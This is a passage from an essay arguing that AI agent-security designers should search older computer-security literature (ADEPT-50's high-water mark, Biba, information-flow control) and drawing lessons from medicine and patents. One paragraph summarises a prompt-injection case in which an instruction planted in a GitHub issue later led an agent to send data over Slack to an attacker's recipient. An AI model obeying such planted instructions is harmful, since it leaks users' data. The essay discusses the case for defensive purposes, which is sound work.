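The first query failed because "permission" now mostly refers to phone apps and file settings. One result, *Analysis of Longitudinal Changes in Privacy Behavior of Android Applications* (2021), examines how Android apps' use of permissions changed over time. A typical web result was MITRE's *CWE-732*, a catalogue entry about files that the wrong people can read or change. Neither covers permissions that change depending on what a program has read.

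The remedy is to split the design into parts and list older words for each:

| Part of the design | Modern words | Older words |
|---|---|---|
| What acts | agent, session, task | subject, process, job |
| What it reads | context, private data | object, file, classified information |
| How the system marks the data | protected, sensitive | label, classification, compartment |
| What the agent may do | permissions, scopes | clearance, authority, access rights |
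| What changes after reading | ratchet, one-way switch | floating label, high-water mark, low-water mark, demotion |

A newcomer can fill in the first four rows from a security textbook. Searching with those rows was enough to reach the right field, and one result was a textbook chapter, *Multilevel Security*. It mentions that people increasingly use "information flow control" for policies of this kind, which gives the searcher another term to try. It also reports that the US Defense Department spent several billion dollars on multilevel security research between about 1980 and 2005, so a searcher who reads it has good reason to suspect that somebody has already tried the rule.

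The last row is the hardest to fill in because it contains the name the searcher is looking for. Tables of contents can help. The contents list of *A Guide to Understanding Security Modeling in Trusted Systems* (US National Computer Security Center, 1992) has "Floating Sensitivity Labels" and "The Chinese Wall Security Policy" one page apart, so a reader who looks up either will probably notice the other.

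The fourth query shows that the old papers are easy to find with the right search terms, but it included the names Weissman, Biba and ADEPT-50, which a newcomer to the field might not think to use. Someone starting from the textbook would probably need more attempts, or help from a colleague who recognised the description.

### Following the citations

Landwehr's survey is more useful to an agent designer than the original paper. It covers, in about 39 pages, capability lists, the reference monitor, the high-water mark, Biba's integrity levels and the information-flow work of Fenton and Denning, so a reader can use it to find older work behind five of the seven cases. The other two, SQL injection and the confused deputy, involve later results.

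The survey also contains a warning that applies to the Trust Ratchet. ADEPT-50 tended to classify files too high, so people would have to lower classifications routinely, and Landwehr expected this to make mistakes and deliberate violations harder to detect. Cloudflare's design also lets someone with authority approve a lower classification for data that a new task inherits. If most tasks need that approval, dangerous approvals will be hard to tell from routine ones.

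ADEPT-50 ran at several sites in the Pentagon, and Landwehr reports that its users found it acceptable. His judgement deserves some caution because he based it partly on conversations with Weissman, who had helped to build the system.

Following citations back leads to the source of an idea, but a designer usually needs the later papers that cite that source more, because they describe what happened when people used the idea. MITRE's 1977 report, *Integrity Considerations for Secure Computer Systems*, states Biba's rules, but only the later work on LOMAC describes programs failing because they had lost permissions they still needed.

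### When to stop, and how such searches fail

Researchers can reasonably stop searching when the earliest source they have found presents the idea as its own, a later survey traces the idea to that source, and one more search using the source's vocabulary finds nothing older. This search met the first two conditions. Weissman calls the running records of what a job has opened "important new concepts" and cites nobody for them at that point, and the 1981 survey starts its account of the idea with ADEPT-50. Meeting the third would take another search for terms such as "authority history". Someone who wants to claim priority should do that search, but a designer who only wants to avoid old mistakes could reasonably skip it.

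Even with good search terms, a search can miss a source because the archive doesn't contain it. Preprint servers have few papers from the 1960s and 1970s, so a search limited to them will make the field look younger than it is. Old reports are often scans, and software can misread the print. In the Defense Department's copy of the 1981 survey, the machine-readable text at the top garbles Landwehr's name and gives the subject as "FORMAL MOCLS", so an exact search of that line for "models" would miss it.

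A searcher may also stop too soon, at a rule that only looks the same. ADEPT-50's high-water mark, for example, is only a near match for the ratchet. The searcher can't tell this from the name and has to read how the rule works.

Citations in recent papers can lead researchers to the older literature, even if the papers don't name the rule. *Scan Before You Install* (2026), one of the ten papers on agents, studies weaknesses in "skills", which are add-ons for agents. In one demonstration, an instruction from a GitHub issue stayed in the stored conversation and later came back into the agent's input. The agent was allowed to read its history and send Slack messages, but the user had not authorised it to send what it found to a recipient the attacker chose. The paper cites information-flow research, which is part of the relevant older literature, for the point that permission to read data does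 not limit where a program sends it.

### What medical journals tried

How well researchers use earlier work has been measured more thoroughly in medicine than in most other fields. In *A systematic examination of the citation of prior research*, Robinson and Goodman (2011) took 227 published analyses, each combining at least four clinical trials of the same treatment, and checked what share of the earlier trials each of the 1,523 trials cited. The median share was 21%. Of the trials with at least five predecessors, 23% cited none and another 23% cited only one.

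Robinson and Goodman found that the median number of earlier trials cited was two, however many existed. This suggests that researchers cite enough to show they know the subject and then stop, although Robinson and Goodman could not determine why. They also note that some researchers may have considered earlier trials when planning their own but left them out of the report.

By the time that study appeared, *The Lancet* had already introduced a rule that all reports submitted from 1 August 2010 must set their results against the totality of evidence. The rule, reproduced in Testing Treatments' *Instructions to authors to put research in context*, also required authors to describe how they searched and what their study added. The Lancet journals later adopted a three-part panel called "Research in context", covering the evidence before the study, the study's added value, and the implications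 of all the evidence. According to slides on the panel from the Consortium of Universities for Global Health (CUGH), the first part must list the databases and other sources, the search terms, the exact start and end dates, and the criteria for including studies. The table of queries above records roughly the same details, so the format would transfer to computer security without much change.

It is harder to tell whether the rule worked. Clarke and Hopewell (2013), in *Randomised trial reports continue to be islands of evidence*, examined the 35 trial reports that *The Lancet* and four other leading journals published in May 2012. Only two combined their results with earlier trials in a systematic review, a study that searches for and assesses all the evidence on a question. Twenty made no apparent systematic attempt to put their findings in context. The results varied between journals,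 but the published summary doesn't give figures for each journal, so it doesn't show whether *The Lancet* did better.

*Trends of Randomized Clinical Trials Citing Prior Systematic Reviews, 2007-2021* (Jia, Li and colleagues, 2023) covers 4,003 trials for which a relevant review had been available for at least two years. The share citing any systematic review rose from 35.5% in 2007 and 2008 to 71.8% in 2020 and 2021. In journals that explicitly required such a citation, 61.3% of trials included one, compared with 56.0% in journals with no requirement. After adjusting for other differences, the study found no association between the requirement and citation. Jia and colleagues suspect that journals did not enforce their rules.

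Only 142 of the trials appeared in journals with an explicit requirement, so the 61.3% has a margin of error of about eight percentage points, and a moderate benefit could have gone unnoticed. The general improvement is clear, but explicit rules probably explain little of it, because so few of the trials appeared in journals that had them. Funders had been pressing for the same thing, reporting guidelines recommended it, and more reviews may have become available to cite. The rate was 44.8% for trials with industry funding, compared with 64.0% for those with other outside funding. Company posts on agent security may well have a similar weakness, since the people who write them also work for companies with products to sell.

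A citation also doesn't show that researchers used the review they cited. Jia and colleagues counted any mention of a review, whatever its purpose. *Reports of randomised control trials (RCTs) should begin and conclude with up-to-date systematic reviews of other relevant trials* summarises studies that measured actual use. On average, 17% of new studies had used a systematic review in their design, and about 31% had placed their results in the context of existing studies.

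Few journals have followed *The Lancet* in requiring a prior systematic review. *The use of systematic reviews for conducting new studies in physiotherapy research* compared journals' instructions to authors and found this requirement at four of 14 leading journals, all in the Lancet group, and at none of 149 physiotherapy journals.

The time required is part of the reason. *Setting new research in the context of previous research* (Glasziou, Jones and Clarke, 2023) describes three ways to compare a new trial with earlier ones. A full updated review can take months. Adding the new trial to the data of an existing review is much quicker, and adding it to that review's overall result is quicker still. In the paper's example, six trials of lower blood-pressure targets had suggested a 9% reduction in risk, with a margin of error that included zero benefit. Adding one new trial raised the estimate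 to 14%, and the margin of error no longer included zero benefit. Citing the earlier review alone would not have shown readers this change.

Security papers have no common measure that researchers could combine in this way. The closest equivalent is to run an old attack or counterexample against the new design. Fenton's program is a few lines long, and anyone who had tried it on CaMeL's interpreter before publication would have found the leak.

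### Patents and the duty to disclose

US patent law requires inventors, their lawyers and others closely involved in an application to tell the patent office about any information, including earlier work, that they know to be material to whether the invention deserves a patent. A court can refuse to enforce the whole patent if it finds that they withheld important information to deceive the office.

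The duty to disclose covers only what people already know. It does not require them to search, and an inventor might even prefer not to. It therefore addresses concealment, whereas most of the missing references in agent security seem to result from ignorance or habit.

The penalty also encourages applicants to submit long lists of references to protect themselves, which can bury the important ones. Cotropia, Lemley and Sampat found in *Do Applicant Patent Citations Matter?* (2013) that when examiners rejected claims, they relied almost entirely on documents they had found themselves rather than on these lists. A long list is of little use unless someone explains which items matter and why.

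In October 2025 the US patent office began a pilot in which software searches for earlier work before an examiner reviews a patent application. The applicant receives a ranked list of up to ten documents and can narrow the claims or abandon the application, but doesn't have to respond. This approach suits agent papers better than a duty to disclose, because it gives authors the references while they can still change the design. It would be harder to apply to agent papers than to patents, though, because the patent office can search using a precise written claim, and agent papers rarely state so exactly what is new.

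### What computing conferences ask

Machine learning conferences ask authors a lot about their experiments and little about earlier work. The 2025 checklist for NeurIPS, one of the largest, had 16 questions on matters such as limitations, proofs, computing resources and statistical significance. None was about how authors had looked for earlier results. The closest was about whether they had credited the creators of the code, data and models they used.

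The task falls to reviewers instead. NeurIPS asked them whether a paper makes clear how it differs from previous contributions. ICML, another large conference, asked for more in its 2025 form, which had one box for how the paper relates to the broader literature and another for essential references it fails to discuss. But a reviewer can name a missing reference only if they already know of it or find it. If author and reviewer both come from machine learning, neither is likely to think of Biba.

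### Literature search by AI

Language models can match descriptions by meaning, which should help people who do not know the old name for an idea. In October 2025, for example, Mark Sellke and Mehtaab Sawhney used thousands of queries to OpenAI's GPT-5 to search the literature for solutions to Paul Erdős's problems, which the mathematician Thomas Bloom lists on a website. They found published solutions to ten problems that the site listed as open.

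Kevin Weil, an OpenAI vice-president, then announced that GPT-5 had solved ten previously unsolved problems. Bloom called this "a dramatic misrepresentation", since "open" on his site meant only that he did not know of a solution. Weil deleted the post. The search had worked well, but Weil had treated problems as unsolved because Bloom did not know of a solution. Researchers make the same mistake when they claim an idea is new because they do not know of earlier work on it.

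A model can also rediscover a result by itself. In January 2026 GPT-5.2 Pro produced a proof for number 281 on Bloom's list, and a reader then pointed out that the result followed from two older theorems. Erdős had apparently missed the connection, although he helped to prove one of the theorems in 1936.

Automated checks for novelty have a worse record. Beel, Kan and Baumgart (2025) evaluated the AI Scientist, a Sakana AI system that proposes ideas, runs experiments and writes papers. The system judged novelty with simple keyword searches and classed some well-established techniques as new, including micro-batching (training a model on a few examples at a time). In *All That Glitters is Not Novel* (2025), Gupta and Pruthi asked 13 experts to look for the sources of 50 AI-written research documents. The experts found that 24% of the documents either paraphrased the method of an existing work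 or borrowed heavily from one without acknowledging it. Automated plagiarism detectors were poor at catching this.

The systems in those two studies are old, and current models would probably do better. But it will still be easier to confirm that an older result exists than to establish that none does. If a model cites a 1969 paper by Weissman for a similar rule, a designer can read the paper and decide. AI search is therefore a good way to collect candidates, but a poor basis for claiming to be first, because when it finds nothing, the designer learns only that one search failed.

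The Erdős problems were also easier to search for in one respect, because each came with an exact statement. An agent designer has to describe the mechanism without using its new name, because a model given that name may just return other recent papers that use it.

Researchers could test a search tool on the seven cases by giving it a plain description of each modern design and checking whether it returns the older result. The tool should search only documents that don't already connect the two. The test should also include some designs that have no close precedent, to measure how often the tool wrongly reports one.

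### A statement of the nearest older result

Authors could add a few sentences to each paper that name the closest earlier result, explain the difference and list the search terms they used. For the Trust Ratchet, the statement might read:

> The closest older result is the high-water mark in ADEPT-50 (1969), together with Bell and LaPadula's ban on writing to a lower level. Our rule removes whichever permissions are listed in the policy, instead of following a ranking of levels. It also withholds the data until the new restrictions are in force on every machine. We searched for "floating label", "high-water mark" and "history-based access control".

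Finding similar earlier work and stating how a new design differs from it might take a day of searching and a paragraph in the paper. The comparison would help readers find the design's known weaknesses and give reviewers something specific to check. Authors who cannot state a difference would learn that they may have reinvented something.

The evidence from medicine supports the objection that authors will add a token citation and move on. Asking them to explain how their design differs from the older work makes that harder, because they have to understand the older work to do it. Zhang and colleagues name the old principle that each part of AgentSandbox is meant to serve. For example, they tie least privilege to using a fresh agent for each task and discarding it afterwards. But they don't say where their design departs from the principles. That explanation would have had to include the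 fact that nobody can verify AgentSandbox's prompt-based filters.

Enforcement also matters, given what Jia and colleagues suspected about journals. A conference could require the statement from a random half of its submissions on agent security, then ask specialists to count the important older results that each half missed. Comparing the two halves would give a clearer answer than medicine has and would take one reviewing cycle.

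### A table of old and new terms

A shared table would help at the point where the worked search nearly got stuck, the older name for the central idea. It might begin like this:

| New term | Older terms to search for | Where the match fails |
|---|---|---|
| Trust ratchet, one-way switch | High-water mark, floating label, Chinese Wall | ADEPT-50's mark affected only new files |
| Prompt injection | SQL injection, Trojan horse, confused deputy | A model does not finish reading its instructions before the data arrives |
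| Capabilities, in CaMeL | Labels, information-flow control | A lost token removes a right, but a lost label may set data free |
| Policy on tool calls | Reference monitor, security kernel | People with authority set the old policies in advance |
| Narrowing a delegated permission | Attenuation, grant | The 1966 version needed one supervisor on one machine |

A few specialists could draft fifty rows of the table in a week. Keeping it current would take longer, and such projects tend to go out of date when their founders lose interest. A professional society or an existing catalogue of weaknesses could host the table, with a named editor and a date on each row.

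The more serious danger is that a table encourages false analogies, like the one with SQL injection that David C warned about. The third column is meant to prevent that, so editors should leave out any pair for which nobody can fill it in. The table would also help AI search tools.

### Security reviewers and joint workshops

Conferences could assign one security specialist to each paper that proposes a defence for agents. Patent examiners rely on documents they find themselves, which suggests that an informed outsider helps more than a longer list of references from the author. f-secure and FIDES also show how much it helps to have someone on the team who already knows the literature.

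Expertise in security is too broad a qualification for a reviewer who is meant to catch missing older work. StruQ went through review at a leading security conference without gaining any older references, and an expert on identity standards may know no more about Fenton than a machine learning researcher does. An editor would have to match the reviewer to the paper's mechanism, which means finding an information-flow specialist for a paper that labels data. Such specialists are scarce, and waiting for them could delay publication in a field where a few months matter. The conference could limit the delay by asking them only which older result is closest and leaving the rest of the review to others. For most papers, a specialist could answer that in an hour or so.

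Blogs have no such reviewers. A blogger can instead show a draft to one specialist, or publish the post and correct it openly when a reader points out a precedent, as Willison did with Chromium's rule.

Joint workshops would bring the fields together more directly. Christodorescu and colleagues argue that computer security and AI agent security need to co-operate, and their team included people from Google, Meta and several universities, as well as an independent researcher who attacks commercial agents. Workshops take travel, organisers' time and a few days of everyone's attention. Their benefits are hard to measure, and they tend to attract people who already agree that the other field matters. To get more out of them, organisers could ask each designer to describe one unpublished mechanism without naming it, then have specialists from several branches of security identify the nearest thing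 they know. The answers could go into the table of terms, so that people who did not attend could use them too.
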